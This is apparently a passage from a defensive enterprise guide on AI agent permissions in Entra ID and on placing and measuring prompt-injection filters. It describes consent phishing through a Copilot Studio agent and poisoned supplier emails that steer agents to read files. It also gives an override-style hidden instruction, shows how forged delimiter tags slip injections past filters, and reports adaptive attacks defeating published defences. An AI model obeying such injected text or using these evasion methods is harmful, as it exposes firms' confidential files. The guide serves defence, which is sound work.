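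A firm can close these gaps by not letting employees consent at all. According to Maester, a tool that checks Microsoft security settings, the baseline of the US cybersecurity agency CISA requires this for third-party applications, while Microsoft recommends letting employees consent to selected permissions for applications from verified publishers. CISA's rule is easier to maintain because nobody has to follow the growing list, but even a harmless request has to wait for an administrator. For a firm whose agents read supplier mail, CISA's rule is probably the better starting point, with exceptions for applications that ask only for a user's name and sign-in.

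### Why administrators remain exposed

None of the 36 restrictions protects the administrators who approve applications, because of how Entra ID combines policies. A consent policy approves a request that matches at least one of its inclusion conditions and none of its exclusion conditions, if any. When several policies apply to one person, a request needs approval from only one of them, and an exclusion in one has no effect on the others.

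The restrictions are exclusions in the consent policy for ordinary users. A second policy lets an Application Administrator consent to delegated permissions for any application, and to application permissions other than those of Microsoft Graph. The administrator therefore sees an "Accept" button for requests that an ordinary user would be refused.

Datadog Security Labs showed how an attacker could exploit this by building an agent in Copilot Studio. The agent's page had a genuine Microsoft address and looked much like Microsoft's own assistant, but its login button led to a consent screen for an application the researchers controlled. An attacker targeting an ordinary employee first needed an account inside the firm, while one targeting an Application Administrator needed no access to the firm and could request any delegated permission. The agent then forwarded the victim's token from Microsoft's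 servers, so the victim's own web traffic showed no connection to the attacker.

More people can now make this mistake. In autumn 2025, a Global Administrator, the most powerful role in a tenant, still had to consent to an agent's permissions before an AI Administrator could deploy it (Microsoft, 2025). Under Microsoft's *AI Admin RBAC updates*, which rolled out in March 2026, AI Administrators can grant consent for the whole tenant themselves, except for Graph's application permissions. The change usefully reduces everyday use of the Global Administrator account, but a firm with six AI Administrators now has six more people to protect.

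Such a firm should assign few of these roles and give their holders separate accounts that receive no ordinary mail. Those holders should open consent requests only from the approval queue, never from a link they are sent. Datadog Security Labs also advises setting an alert on the log event "Consent to application" and changing the default that lets every employee register new applications. Without that change, an attacker who takes over one employee's account can create an application inside the firm and offer it to colleagues.

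### An approval procedure

When Entra ID blocks the clerk's mail assistant, she should be able to request approval for it. According to Microsoft, she can do this only if the firm has set up the admin consent workflow, which sends her request to chosen administrators. Without this workflow, some users would probably paste the mail into an unapproved website.

The procedure could run as follows.

1. **Request.** The clerk explains what the assistant will do and who will use it. The head of purchasing agrees to be its owner.

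2. **Publisher.** The reviewer finds out which company is behind the name. A "verified publisher" mark means that Microsoft has confirmed the company's identity. It doesn't mean that Microsoft has tested the software.

3. **Permissions.** The reviewer compares the requested permissions with the job. The vendor wants to change mail and read all files, but sorting supplier mail requires neither. Since the consent screen presents the list as a whole, the reviewer may have to ask the vendor for a version that wants less. Microsoft's administration pages show a risk rating for each permission. The rating that Microsoft (2025) added for Teams applications informs the reviewer but blocks nothing, and a general rating can't reflect what is in this firm's contracts folder.

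4. **Data.** The reviewer asks where the vendor stores the mail, for how long, and whether it trains models on it. The three-capability test belongs here too, since an assistant that reads outside mail and private files may also be able to send.

5. **Decision and scope.** The firm approves the assistant for 30 purchasing staff instead of all 5,000 employees and records its reasons.

6. **Expiry and review.** Since consent has no end date, the owner sets one, perhaps in six months. At that point, logs may show that nobody uses the assistant or that it never uses one of its permissions.

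7. **Revocation.** An administrator removes the grant and blocks the application from signing in. An access token may continue to work for up to an hour or so, and the vendor keeps any mail it has already copied unless the firm has it deleted.

For agents with their own Entra identities, Microsoft can automate the expiry through access packages, which are bundles of permissions with rules about who may request them. An administrator sets the approvers and the duration, according to Semperis, an identity security company. Each agent also has a sponsor, an employee who is accountable for its purpose. Microsoft notifies the sponsor before the access ends, and an extension requires a new approval. If the sponsor leaves the company, Entra ID makes the sponsor's manager responsible, although the manager may know nothing about the agent.

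### Who should decide

Entra ID determines who can make a grant, which is a different question from who should. An Application Administrator may be able to open the contracts folder to an assistant without knowing what the folder contains. The invented firm could divide the decisions this way:

| Request | Who decides |
| --- | --- |
| Sign-in and the user's name | The employee, within the consent policy |
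| Delegated permission to read mail, files or chats | An AI or Application Administrator, after the head of the department that owns the data agrees |
| Delegated permission to send messages or change records | The same people, plus the security team |
| Any application permission | The data's owner and the security team together, with a Global Administrator making the grant if it concerns Graph |
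| Permission to manage roles, applications or their credentials | The firm refuses, unless the head of security approves a written exception |

The division is based on how much damage an injection could do, so reading one person's mail ranks below sending mail as that person. It also prevents anyone who wants an agent from approving it alone.

### Entra Agent ID: blueprints and identities

A firm with dozens of similar agents would repeat this procedure many times. Microsoft's Entra Agent ID gives agents their own kind of identity in the directory and lets an administrator approve a whole class of them together. It uses three main objects:

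- A blueprint is the template for one class of agent. It holds the credentials and the permission settings.
- A blueprint principal represents the blueprint inside one tenant. Administrators attach their grants for the class to it.
- An agent identity is the account of a single agent. It has no password or certificate of its own, so the blueprint uses its credentials to obtain tokens for it.

Microsoft also separates what a developer configures from what an administrator grants. In the declared permissions, which Microsoft calls "required resource access", the developer lists what the agent needs, and administrators see this list when they review the agent. The inheritable permissions setting specifies the services, such as Microsoft Graph, for which agents may inherit permissions from their blueprint. Neither setting gives an agent access until an administrator grants consent to the blueprint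 principal or to a single agent identity.

The effective permissions are the ones that Entra ID writes into the agent's token:

effective = direct grants ∪ (grants on the blueprint principal ∩ inheritable permissions)

An agent has the permissions that an administrator granted to it directly, plus any that an administrator granted to its blueprint and the developer made inheritable. When using delegated permissions, the agent also cannot access anything the user cannot.

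While running, an application can request permissions that its developer never declared. If an administrator accepts, the application's agents can inherit those permissions. A reviewer therefore can't assume that a list of declared permissions saved months earlier still covers everything the agents are permitted to do.

### One grant that reaches 40 agents

Suppose the invented firm builds a "Supplier mail" blueprint and creates 40 agent identities from it, one for each category of goods. The developer makes delegated Graph permissions inheritable. In June, an administrator grants the blueprint principal Mail.Read, the permission to read the user's mail.

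each of the 40 agents: ∅ ∪ ({Mail.Read} ∩ all delegated Graph permissions) = {Mail.Read}

One decision has replaced 40, and in this case it is the right one, because every agent needs to read mail.

In September, the clerk who buys steel wants her agent to compare invoices with contracts. The administrator grants Files.Read.All, which covers all files the user can open, again on the blueprint principal. The steel agent now has both Mail.Read and Files.Read.All, and so do the 39 other agents, which don't need to read files. Any agent the firm creates in October will have both permissions from its first day. Microsoft's *Configure inheritable permissions for agent identity blueprints* confirms that the "all allowed" setting automatically includes permissions granted later.

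All 40 agents read email from strangers. Until September, a poisoned message could make the timber agent access only mail. Since then, such a message can also make it access any file that the clerk using it may open. If the administrator had granted the file permission as an application permission, and the developer had made application permissions inheritable too, each of the 40 agents could read files across the whole firm.

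The administrator should have granted Files.Read.All directly on the steel agent's identity:

steel agent: {Files.Read.All} ∪ {Mail.Read}

the other 39: {Mail.Read}

For highly privileged agents, Microsoft suggests leaving the service out of the inheritable list, so that each installation requires a new decision. Here that would also stop the agents from inheriting Mail.Read, because both permissions belong to Graph. A list of individual permissions would solve this, but Microsoft's documentation is inconsistent on whether developers can use one. Its management guide recommends starting with such a list, while its newer configuration page offers only all permissions or none. Semperis found the option in the documentation for Graph's beta version. A firm that doesn't want to depend on a beta feature can create a second blueprint for agents that read contracts.

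A blueprint also makes it easier to stop agents in an emergency. If the security team disables the blueprint, Microsoft prevents all 40 agents from signing in. But enabling it again restores the same access, so the team also has to remove the mistaken grant.

### Consent screens and visible permissions

When a clerk uses one of these agents, a separate application, such as the chat window, signs her in and receives a token. The blueprint exchanges this token for one that carries the agent's identity and the clerk's delegated permissions. According to *Agent On Behalf Of Oauth Flow*, part of Microsoft's documentation, the original token must name the blueprint as its recipient, and Entra ID rejects tokens meant for other services.

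The agent can't open a consent screen during this process. *Agent On Behalf Of Oauth Flow* (revised August 2026) explains that a user who tries to consent for an agent identity gets an error. An administrator has to approve the delegated permissions on the blueprint in advance.

Another Microsoft guide, which *Microsoft Entra Documentation Changes* (2026) recorded in June, includes a step for "user or admin authorization" of interactive agents. The two pages are probably compatible. Microsoft's *Agent Identities, Blueprints, and Users* describes a return address on the blueprint used only to record consent, so a user's consent would attach to the blueprint rather than the individual agent. The August revision specifies that the error occurs on the "child identity", which fits this reading.

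This removes one opportunity for consent phishing, since nobody can trick a clerk into accepting permissions for an individual agent identity. It also means the clerk may never see a list of what her agent can do, so the firm has to tell her.

Administrators have also had trouble seeing that list. In May 2026, Microsoft's documentation stated that inherited permissions did not appear on an agent identity in the Entra admin center or through Graph, and were visible only inside tokens. In the 40-agent example, an auditor who opened the timber agent's record in October would see neither Mail.Read nor Files.Read.All.

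This has partly changed. Semperis found two new fields in the beta version of Graph that list an agent's inherited permissions. The stable version, v1.0, lacked them, so an audit tool that uses it could still report too little access. Until the firm knows which version its tool reads, it should take the grants from the blueprint principal and the inheritable settings from the blueprint, and apply the formula above.

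### Blueprint owners and outside vendors

Entra ID blocks certain high-risk permissions for agents, but an approver can't rely on it to catch every dangerous request. Compass Security tried to assign 1,041 permissions to agent identities. Entra ID blocked 97 and allowed 944, including six Graph application permissions that Compass Security considers could lead to control of the whole tenant. In one case, Entra ID blocked a permission but allowed another with a similar effect.

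The approver also has to check who owns the blueprint. Compass Security found that an owner could add a new credential to a blueprint and then act as any of its agents. Microsoft makes the developer who creates a blueprint its owner, so in the example, anyone who takes over that developer's account could use all 40 agents and any application permissions they hold. Before approving a powerful blueprint, the firm should transfer ownership to a well-protected administrative account.

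A vendor's blueprint creates a related problem because the vendor keeps the credentials, even after the firm adds a blueprint principal to its own tenant. Anyone who obtains those credentials can create agents in the firm's tenant with the permissions the firm approved, so the firm relies on the vendor to protect the credentials for as long as the approval lasts. Compass Security advises customers to verify the publisher, permissions and business purpose before approving a blueprint, and to avoid high-impact permissions unless there is a clear need and someone monitors their use. If the firm ends the contract, it can remove the blueprint by deleting the principal.

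### Connectors in other assistants

The same question applies to other assistants' connectors, which are ready-made links to mailboxes, file stores and other services. Google Workspace controls access where the data is held. An administrator can trust an outside application, limit it to certain Google data or block it. ChatGPT Enterprise and the business plans of Claude, Anthropic's assistant, control access in the assistant. An administrator enables a connector for the organisation, and each employee then signs in to the connected service.

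A firm that keeps its files with Google and uses Claude has to check the settings in both Google Workspace and Claude. A block in Google Workspace applies even if the connector is enabled in Claude. It also stops employees from connecting personal Claude accounts to the firm's files, which disabling the connector in the firm's Claude account does not do.

If 500 employees each connect an assistant to four MCP servers, they can face 2,000 separate consent decisions. An MCP extension called enterprise-managed authorization moves those decisions to the company's identity provider, the service that signs employees in. The assistant requests a signed statement from the identity provider that the employee may use the server. If company policy allows it, the assistant exchanges the statement for an access token at the server's own authorisation service, and the employee sees no extra screen. An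 administrator can then decide once for each server and withdraw approval centrally. The assistant, identity provider and server must all support the extension, so a firm should test its own combination before relying on it.

### An approved agent can still follow an attacker

Suppose the firm has done all this correctly for its purchasing agent. It knows the publisher, the head of purchasing has agreed to each permission, and the approval expires in six months. The agent then opens the poisoned email from the fake supplier and searches for price agreements. Its token is valid and covers the contracts folder, so Graph returns the files.

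Entra ID allows the request because it checks only the agent's identity and permissions, not the text of the email. To catch the hidden instruction, the firm has to inspect that text before the model acts on it.

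## Choosing and placing prompt filters

A prompt filter can do that inspection, but even a good one is of little use if it doesn't receive the text that needs checking. With some common settings, the cloud vendors' filters never receive the tool results that carry indirect injections.

### How a filter reaches a decision

Engineers train most prompt filters on examples of attacks and of harmless text. Microsoft trains Prompt Shields on known injection techniques in several languages and updates it as new ones appear. For a supplier's email, the process could run like this:

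1. The agent's software extracts the email's text, including HTML comments and anything else the model would receive.
2. It normalises the text by removing invisible characters and decoding encoded passages.
3. The classifier splits the text into tokens and calculates a score between 0 and 1. A higher score means a closer resemblance to an attack.
4. The software compares the score with the firm's thresholds, then blocks the email, flags it for a person or passes it to the model.

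Prompt injection filters have to extract text differently from ordinary phishing filters. Microsoft (2026) explains that its mail filter can take a picture of a message and extract the visible words, which defeats spammers' invisible characters. But that picture would not show an injection hidden in an HTML comment, so an injection filter has to check the text that the model will receive.

Normalisation matters because an invisible character inside a word can change the tokens that the classifier receives. Blocking every message with such characters would block harmless ones too. Microsoft's first rule for one range of them also caught messages containing the flag emojis of England, Scotland and Wales, which use characters from that range.

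The firm could set two thresholds for the score s:

```
block   if s ≥ 0.8
flag    if 0.5 ≤ s < 0.8
pass    if s < 0.5
```

With invented scores, four emails might turn out as follows:

| Email | Score | Result |
| --- | --- | --- |
| A supplier confirms an order | 0.03 | Pass |
| A supplier asks the firm to ignore its previous email and use the new order form | 0.62 | Flag, although the email is harmless |
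| A hidden comment tells AI assistants to ignore their rules and send all files | 0.97 | Block |
| The poisoned email presents the request for price agreements as normal onboarding | 0.41 | Pass |

Lowering the flag threshold to 0.4 would catch the poisoned email. It would also send more ordinary supplier mail to a clerk, so the firm should test thresholds on its own mail before relying on them.

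Products differ in how much of the scoring they expose. AWS's *Use the InvokeGuardrailChecks API in your application* describes an interface that returns a score and leaves the threshold and the action to the developer. In an ordinary Amazon Bedrock guardrail, the developer chooses a filter strength of None, Low, Medium or High. The two scales run in opposite directions, since a "High" strength means more filtering and a high numerical threshold means less.

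Prompt Shields returns two true-or-false values, "detected" and "filtered". If "detected" is true and "filtered" is false, the classifier detected an attack but the model still received it.

A classifier also can't determine from the wording alone whether the writer was allowed to give an instruction. AWS's *Detect prompt attacks with Amazon Bedrock Guardrails* gives the example of a bank's developer telling the model that it is a banking assistant, and an attacker then telling it that it is a chemistry expert. The two instructions have much the same form, so the application has to tell the filter which one came from the user.

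### Spotlighting: marking text for the model

A filter will miss some attacks. Spotlighting, Microsoft's method of marking outside text, is meant to make the model less likely to follow the ones that get through. Here are its three modes applied to the harmless sentence "Please confirm order 4471."

| Mode | What the model receives | What the system prompt explains |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Delimiting | `<<k7Q2 Please confirm order 4471. k7Q2>>` | Text between these markers contains no instructions for the model |
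| Datamarking | `Please^confirm^order^4471.` | Text with ^ between the words contains no instructions for the model |
| Encoding | `UGxlYXNlIGNvbmZpcm0gb3JkZXIgNDQ3MS4=` | The model should decode this text and use it only as information |

Delimiting is the easiest to add, but the marker has to be random. An attacker who knows the closing marker can write it into an email, and whatever follows will seem to come from the firm. Datamarking has no single boundary to forge, because the marks run through the whole text. Encoding sets the email apart clearly, but the model must be able to decode it reliably.

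Encoding also makes the text longer. The example grows from 26 characters to 36, and long documents can exceed the model's input limit. Microsoft doesn't charge for Spotlighting itself, but customers pay for the additional tokens.

Microsoft offers the encoding mode in Foundry as a preview. It is off by default and works only with models that an application calls through the Chat Completions interface. The model sometimes mentions base64 in its answer, a known side effect that may confuse users who only asked for a summary.

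Spotlighting doesn't block anything or raise an alert. If the purchasing agent uses it with a filter, the filter should inspect the email before the software encodes it.

### Which text the three cloud filters inspect

Microsoft's Prompt Shields has separate checks for attacks that users type and attacks in documents. The document check can inspect user input and tool results, so it suits an agent that fetches supplier mail through a tool, provided an administrator selects "tool response" as a checkpoint and assigns the settings to the agent. The administrator also chooses whether to block a detected attack or only annotate it.

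Microsoft suggests exempting trusted sources from the document check to reduce false alarms. But if the purchasing department exempted everyone in the supplier directory, an attacker who took over a supplier's mailbox would face no filter in the agent.

Google's filter is Model Armor. Google Cloud's *Integrate Model Armor with Gemini Enterprise* explains how to connect it to Google's workplace assistant, Gemini Enterprise. An administrator creates a template of filter settings and turns on the connection. Model Armor then screens users' prompts, the assistant's replies, and the documents and images that users upload directly. If one image inside a document violates the policy, the assistant discards the whole document.

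This integration covers Google's own agents and those that employees make with Google's Agent Designer, but not custom agents, including ones that developers build with Google's Agent Development Kit. If the firm's developers had written the purchasing agent, they would have to send text to Model Armor from their own code. Google's list of screened content also doesn't include documents that the assistant retrieves or results from tools, so Model Armor may not check them.

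The coverage of Amazon Bedrock Guardrails depends on how the application calls the model. A developer who uses the InvokeModel interface has to put tags around the text that needs checking. The guardrail ignores everything outside the tags, and if there are no tags, it doesn't check for prompt attacks.

AWS's *Apply tags to user input to filter content* suggests that checking only the user's question may be enough if the retrieved documents come from trusted sources. The purchasing agent's user is an employee, but its documents come from strangers, so the developer must tag the email for the guardrail to check it. AWS also recommends using a new random tag for every request. If the tag never changed, an attacker could write the closing tag into an email and put the injection after it, where the guardrail would not check it.

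The Converse interface has a different gap. According to AWS's *Include a guardrail with the Converse API*, a guardrail in the request's settings checks the prompts and the model's replies, but not tool results, tool descriptions or the arguments in the model's tool calls. If the purchasing agent fetches the poisoned email with a tool, the guardrail never receives it, even though an administrator would see an active guardrail. The developer has to add another check after the tool returns, for example with InvokeGuardrailChecks, which is available in seven AWS regions.

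AWS defines prompt attacks as user prompts, and all its examples are things a user might type. The same classifier may also recognise instructions in an email, but the firm should test that before depending on it.

| | Prompt Shields in Foundry | Model Armor in Gemini Enterprise | Bedrock Guardrails |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| User prompts | Yes | Yes | Yes, but InvokeModel requires tags |
| Retrieved documents | Yes, with the document check on | Google lists only files that users upload | Only if the application includes them in the text it submits for checking |
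| Tool results | Yes, at the "tool response" checkpoint | Google does not list them | Not through Converse settings; the application needs a separate check |
| Agents the firm wrote itself | Yes, once the firm assigns the settings | No | Yes |
| Default to watch | Spotlighting is off | No screening until an administrator connects a template | The less robust Classic tier |

### Languages, length and price

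The Classic tier of Amazon Bedrock Guardrails supports only English, French and Spanish. According to AWS's *Tailor responsible AI with new safeguard tiers in Amazon Bedrock Guardrails* (2025), Classic was the default, while the Standard tier supported more than 60 languages. AWS's *Languages supported by Amazon Bedrock Guardrails* warns that guardrails are ineffective in unsupported languages. A firm that kept the default could have a filter that works on its English email but barely works on a supplier's email in German.

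AWS's *Safeguard tiers for guardrails policies* also describes the Standard tier as more reliable against prompt attacks. But this tier uses cross-region inference, so AWS may process the text in another region. A firm with rules about where its data may go has to check the list of possible destinations first.

Google sets no direct limit on text length when Model Armor works with Gemini Enterprise, but quotas restrict how much it can process over time. Microsoft's guide to Prompt Shields and AWS's guide to prompt-attack detection do not give a maximum length. If a filter has a limit, the application should split long documents into overlapping pieces, so that an instruction that crosses a boundary appears whole in at least one piece. For example, a 60,000-character contract needs seven checks if each piece has 10,000 characters and shares 1,000 with the next.

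None of the three vendors' set-up guides for these filters lists a price. When the invented firm asks for quotes, it should give the number of texts it wants to check. That number will be much larger than the number of questions its employees ask, because each of the firm's 40,000 daily tool calls can return text that needs checking.

### When the filter is unavailable

If a filter doesn't respond, an application can fail open, which means it passes the text to the model anyway, or fail closed, which means it stops until the filter works again. Google offers both modes for Model Armor but excludes blocked queries from its service guarantee in either mode, so a firm that chooses to fail closed may have no claim against Google if Model Armor blocks its users during an outage.

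Microsoft's and AWS's guides do not describe what happens in an outage, so the firm should build its own safeguard. Prompt Shields returns its findings in the same response as the model's output. The purchasing agent's software can check for those findings and refuse to run any tool call if they are missing. The model may still have read an unchecked email, but that email can't make it search files or send anything.

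Failing closed is reasonable for supplier mail, because an email can usually wait an hour for the agent and a clerk can open it in the meantime. The firm could fail open for a clerk's own typed request and record the gap in filtering. The clerk already has access to the files the agent may open for her, and the rules on recipients and attachments still apply.

### Inside the application or at the model endpoint

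A developer can call the filter from the application's own code, where the source of each text is still available. The application can then apply different checks to text from a clerk and text from a stranger's email. AWS describes three such checkpoints: a full guardrail at the first, a lighter check suited to the particular tool at the second, and a check for unwanted content in the tool's output at the third. To keep delays short, AWS recommends combining guardrails with quick deterministic checks, such as whether a value has the right format.

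For example, if the purchasing agent looks up an order number, ordinary code can verify that the result contains only digits. A result that passes can't carry a hidden instruction, so it doesn't need a classifier. An email body has no fixed format, so it needs the full check.

The weakness of this placement is that every development team has to add the calls. If one team forgets to add the check after a new tool, nothing else in the application will compensate. The filter also can't inspect anything in assistants the firm didn't write.

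A firm can instead attach the filter to the model endpoint, the address where the cloud service receives requests for a model. The firm then configures the filter once for all the applications that use that endpoint. Developers don't have to remember to call the filter, although they may have to tag the text or select the right checkpoints, as described above.

A filter at one provider's endpoint can't inspect requests sent to another provider's model. A firm can instead filter requests at a proxy, a server that relays them to the models. agentgateway's *AWS Bedrock Guardrails* shows how a proxy can apply Amazon's filter to any vendor's model and return an error if a request or reply violates the policy. An agent could still bypass the proxy by calling its model directly, so the firm has to block direct calls in its firewall.

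The endpoint also receives text only after the application has assembled it. If the developer has pasted an email into the clerk's request without a tag, the filter receives it all as one user prompt and cannot treat the stranger's email more strictly than the clerk's own words.

### In a network gateway

Employees also use AI services in the browser, where the firm controls neither the application nor the endpoint. Microsoft's AI Gateway inspects prompts on their way from an employee's computer to such a service. It belongs to Global Secure Access, a Microsoft product that routes employees' internet traffic through Microsoft's network. Microsoft gives these set-up steps:

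1. Turn on the forwarding profile for internet traffic and assign users to it.
2. Set up TLS inspection. TLS is the encryption that protects web traffic, and the gateway can't read a prompt without decrypting it.
3. Install the Global Secure Access client on employees' Windows computers and confirm that their traffic passes through the service.
4. Create a prompt policy and choose the AI services that it covers. For a service that isn't on Microsoft's list, enter the web address that receives the prompts and the position of the prompt within each message.
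5. Add the prompt policy to a security profile.
6. Create a Conditional Access policy, which is a rule in Entra ID about who may use what under which conditions, and have it apply the security profile to the chosen users.

The firm needs a licence for Entra Internet Access, and its Windows computers must belong to its Entra directory. The gateway won't inspect what an employee types into ChatGPT on a private phone.

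In December 2025, when the feature was still a preview, Microsoft documented further limits:

- The gateway inspected typed or pasted text but not files.
- It worked only with applications that send prompts in JSON, a common format for structured data. Microsoft named Gemini as an application that it could not cover.
- It supported prompts of up to 10,000 characters and truncated longer ones.
- When traffic exceeded a rate limit, the gateway blocked further requests.

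Microsoft's *Protect enterprise generative AI applications with Prompt Shield (Preview)* repeats these limits. The length limit is ambiguous, because "truncated" could refer to the copy the gateway scans or to the prompt itself. If only the copy is cut off, an injection after the 10,000th character reaches the model uninspected. If the prompt is cut off, the employee gets an answer based on only part of a document.

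Microsoft has since renamed the feature prompt injection protection, and it revised the guide on 28 August 2026. Entra Diff's *Protect enterprise generative AI apps with prompt injection protection* (2026) records that administrators can now use a Microsoft-managed certificate for TLS inspection, an option the guide did not previously mention. Nair's *How to Protect Generative AI Apps from Prompt Injection* lists Gemini among the supported services, so the earlier restriction probably no longer applies.

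According to Entra Diff's *Ai Prompt Injection Protection* (2026), the guide still listed the JSON requirement for custom applications in July. The limits on files and length may have changed. A firm can check by uploading a file with a harmless test injection, then pasting another after 10,000 characters of ordinary text.

Even without those limits, the gateway would do little to protect the purchasing agent. Microsoft places the inspection between users and model endpoints, so the gateway would check only the clerk's instruction, "deal with the morning's supplier mail". The agent fetches the poisoned email on a server and passes it to the model from there. The gateway also uses Microsoft's jailbreak detection, which is meant to catch attacks in a user's own prompt. The gateway could help if an employee pastes a suspicious email into an outside assistant, but that assistant usually can't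 reach the firm's files unless someone has connected it.

### In the mail system

A mail filter can stop an injection before any assistant reads it, whether that assistant is one of the firm's own agents, Copilot or an outside mail assistant that a clerk has connected. Microsoft has offered such protection since July 2026 in Defender for Office 365, its security service for company email.

The filter first normalises encoded passages, then analyses the subject and body, including hidden text, HTML markup and quoted messages. According to O365Reports, it combines a language model's classification with Defender's other information about the email. If the filter finds an injection, Defender marks the message as high-confidence phishing and quarantines it, so neither the clerk nor her agent can read it.

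The protection is on by default for tenants with Defender for Office 365 Plan 2, which Microsoft includes in its E5 licences. The public preview began in early July. Microsoft first planned general availability for early September, but on 2 September it moved the start and expected completion of that rollout to early October (Microsoft, 2026). Given this delay, a firm should check in October that "Prompt Injection Protection" appears among the detections in its own Defender portal before relying on it.

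The purchasing department's mailbox may also need a Plan 2 licence. Office 365 for IT Pros' *Microsoft Defender for Office 365 Blocks Prompt Injections* (2026) points out that Copilot can read shared mailboxes, and argues that any that receive external mail should have this licence. A purchasing department is likely to use a shared mailbox, and these often have no licence of their own.

A false alarm is more troublesome here than inside the application. If the filter flags a supplier's order form as an attack, the clerk doesn't receive the email and may not know it exists. Only staff with at least the Security Administrator or Compliance Administrator role can review high-confidence phishing in quarantine, and Defender deletes quarantined messages after 15 days by default. Someone with one of those roles should check the quarantine every working day. Microsoft lets administrators report mistakes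 and add exceptions, but an exception for a supplier would also help an attacker who takes over that supplier's mailbox.

The mail filter can't inspect web pages, shared files or the results of other tools. It also checks messages only as they arrive, so it doesn't remove injections already in mailboxes. Attachments may be another gap. Office 365 for IT Pros warns that attackers can hide instructions in them, but O365Reports doesn't list them among the content the filter analyses.

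Microsoft also offers a data-loss prevention rule that stops Copilot from using external email. Unlike the mail filter, this rule applies to messages that have already arrived, and it works without a Plan 2 licence. It would suit the finance director's Copilot if she never needs summaries of outside mail. For purchasing clerks, it would remove most of Copilot's benefit.

### A placement for the purchasing agent

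Suppose the invented firm keeps its mail in Microsoft 365 and runs its purchasing agent on a model in Foundry. It could place its filters as follows:

| Placement | Setting | Reason |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Mail system: Defender for Office 365 | Quarantine, with a Plan 2 licence for the purchasing mailbox | Protects every assistant that reads mail, including those the firm didn't build |
| Agent's tool results: Prompt Shields document check | Block, and carry out no tool call if the finding is missing | Inspects old mail, company files and web pages that the mail filter never receives |
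| Agent's user input: Prompt Shields document check | Block | Clerks sometimes paste a supplier's text into their requests |
| Agent's user input: Prompt Shields user-prompt check | Annotate | Clerks already have the access that the agent uses for them, so a record of attempts is enough at first |
| Network gateway | Add later, for staff who use outside assistants | Cannot inspect the agent's traffic on the server |

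The check in the second row should be set up first. The poisoned email reaches the model as a tool result, and this check covers it however old the message is. The mail filter should come next because it is on by default and needs little beyond licences and someone to review the quarantine.

To save money, the firm could exempt tools that return only its own data, such as stock levels. It should be careful about the supplier directory, though. If suppliers can edit their own entries, one could write an instruction into the company name field, and the agent would read it as part of an apparently internal record.

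Some traffic would still reach a model without inspection:

- Attachments and scanned invoices, unless the agent's software extracts their text and submits it to the filter.
- Mail from before the new protection, when an outside vendor's assistant reads it. That vendor's server fetches the messages directly from Microsoft, so the firm's Prompt Shields settings don't apply.
- Files and web pages that employees open in outside assistants. The gateway would cover some of these at most.
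- Anything that employees enter into AI services on private devices.

The firm can reduce the second gap by denying outside mail assistants access to the purchasing mailbox. For attachments, it can have the agent's software convert each file to text, send the text through Prompt Shields, and leave any file it can't convert for a clerk.

The two Microsoft filters may also share weaknesses, since the same company maintains both. Both could pass the poisoned email because it reads like a routine business request. Before relying on this arrangement, the firm needs to know how many such emails get through and how many real orders end up in quarantine.

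## Measuring what the filters catch and miss

To find out, the firm can take emails that people have already sorted into attacks and harmless messages, run them through the filter and count the results. Three measures come from those counts:

```
detection rate      = attacks flagged ÷ all attacks
false-positive rate = harmless items flagged ÷ all harmless items
precision           = attacks flagged ÷ all items flagged
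```

Research papers often call the detection rate "recall". A vendor can measure the detection and false-positive rates on its own test data. Precision also depends on how many attacks a customer receives, so each customer has to calculate its own.

### False alarms at 20,000 items a day

Suppose 10 of the 20,000 external items that the firm's agents read each day are malicious. The filter has a detection rate of 90% and a false-positive rate of 1%.

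```
true alarms   = 10 × 0.90      = 9
false alarms  = 19,990 × 0.01  ≈ 200
precision     = 9 ÷ (9 + 200)  ≈ 4%
```

A reviewer opens about 23 alarms for every real attack they find. If the filter blocks what it flags, 200 legitimate items a day never reach an agent. A false-positive rate of 0.1% would cut false alarms to about 20 a day and raise precision to about 31%, but the filter would still miss one attack a day.

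The 10 attacks are an assumption. At this volume, the surveys of web pages and résumés described earlier would imply anything from one attack a week to 200 a day, and precision changes enormously over that range:

| Attacks among the items | Precision at 1% false positives | Precision at 0.1% false positives |
| --- | --- | --- |
| 1 a week | 0.06% | 0.6% |
| 10 a day | 4% | 31% |
| 200 a day | 48% | 90% |

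If there is one attack a week, even the better filter raises about 155 false alarms for each attack it catches. A reviewer could work for weeks without seeing a real attack, and would probably start closing alarms without reading them.

### Why a fixed list of attacks flatters a filter

A filter's detection rate depends on which attacks it is tested on. *HiveTraceGuard-Pro* (2026), a paper by the makers of a small filter of that name, reports that the filter caught 99.9% of the injections in the Russian test set and 88% in the English one. Three competing filters caught between 74% and 91% of the Russian set. The paper also discloses that at least 27.1% of the Russian set overlapped with HiveTraceGuard-Pro's training data.

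A list can mislead even without any overlap, because it contains attacks that worked on earlier models. *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) reports attacks on OpenAI's GPT-5 Mini, with no filter, in the AgentDojo benchmark. The benchmark's standard attack never succeeded, but an attack that the researchers' software revised after each failure succeeded in 75% of the scenarios. If a vendor had added a filter to this model and tested it only with the standard attack, the filter would have appeared to stop everything, even though that attack already failed without it.

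### Twelve defences under adaptive attack

Nasr and colleagues, who include researchers at OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind, tested 12 published defences with adaptive attacks, which are revised in response to the defence they face. Some of the defences target jailbreaks and others prompt injection. Most had attack success rates close to zero in their original evaluations. The adaptive attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of them.

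The automated attacks all use the same loop, in which software writes attack texts, tries them on the protected system, scores the results and uses the best ones to write the next batch. In the version used against filters, one language model wrote the variants and another rated their progress from 1 to 10, with a limit of 800 tries per scenario. The researchers also ran a competition with more than 500 participants and $20,000 in prizes.

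These are the results for injection defences protecting Google's Gemini 2.5 Pro:

| Defence | Standard attack succeeds | Adaptive attack succeeds | Median tries before success | Useful tasks completed |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| None | 30% | 100% | 13 | 74% |
| Spotlighting | 28% | 99% | 14 | 75% |
| Model Armor | 28% | 90% | 22 | 59% |
| PromptGuard | 26% | 94% | 21 | 72% |
| Protect AI | 15% | 90% | 30 | 39% |
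| PIGuard | 0% | 71% | 46 | 39% |

The last four are filters. Model Armor hardly reduced the success of the standard attack. Against the adaptive attack, it made the attacker need a few more tries and reduced the user's completed work by about 15 percentage points. PIGuard resisted best, but the agent lost almost half its useful output, which makes it a poor choice for a purchasing department.

The test was harsher than most real attacks in one respect, because the attacking software received the filter's verdict and confidence score after every try. Someone emailing the firm would normally get neither. The results also depended on the model behind the filter. When GPT-5 Mini replaced Gemini, the adaptive attack beat Model Armor in 56% of scenarios, and the median number of tries rose to 76. Google may well have changed the filter since 2025, so 90% may not be its current failure rate. The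 filter's score against the standard attack was almost useless for predicting how it would do against a persistent attacker.

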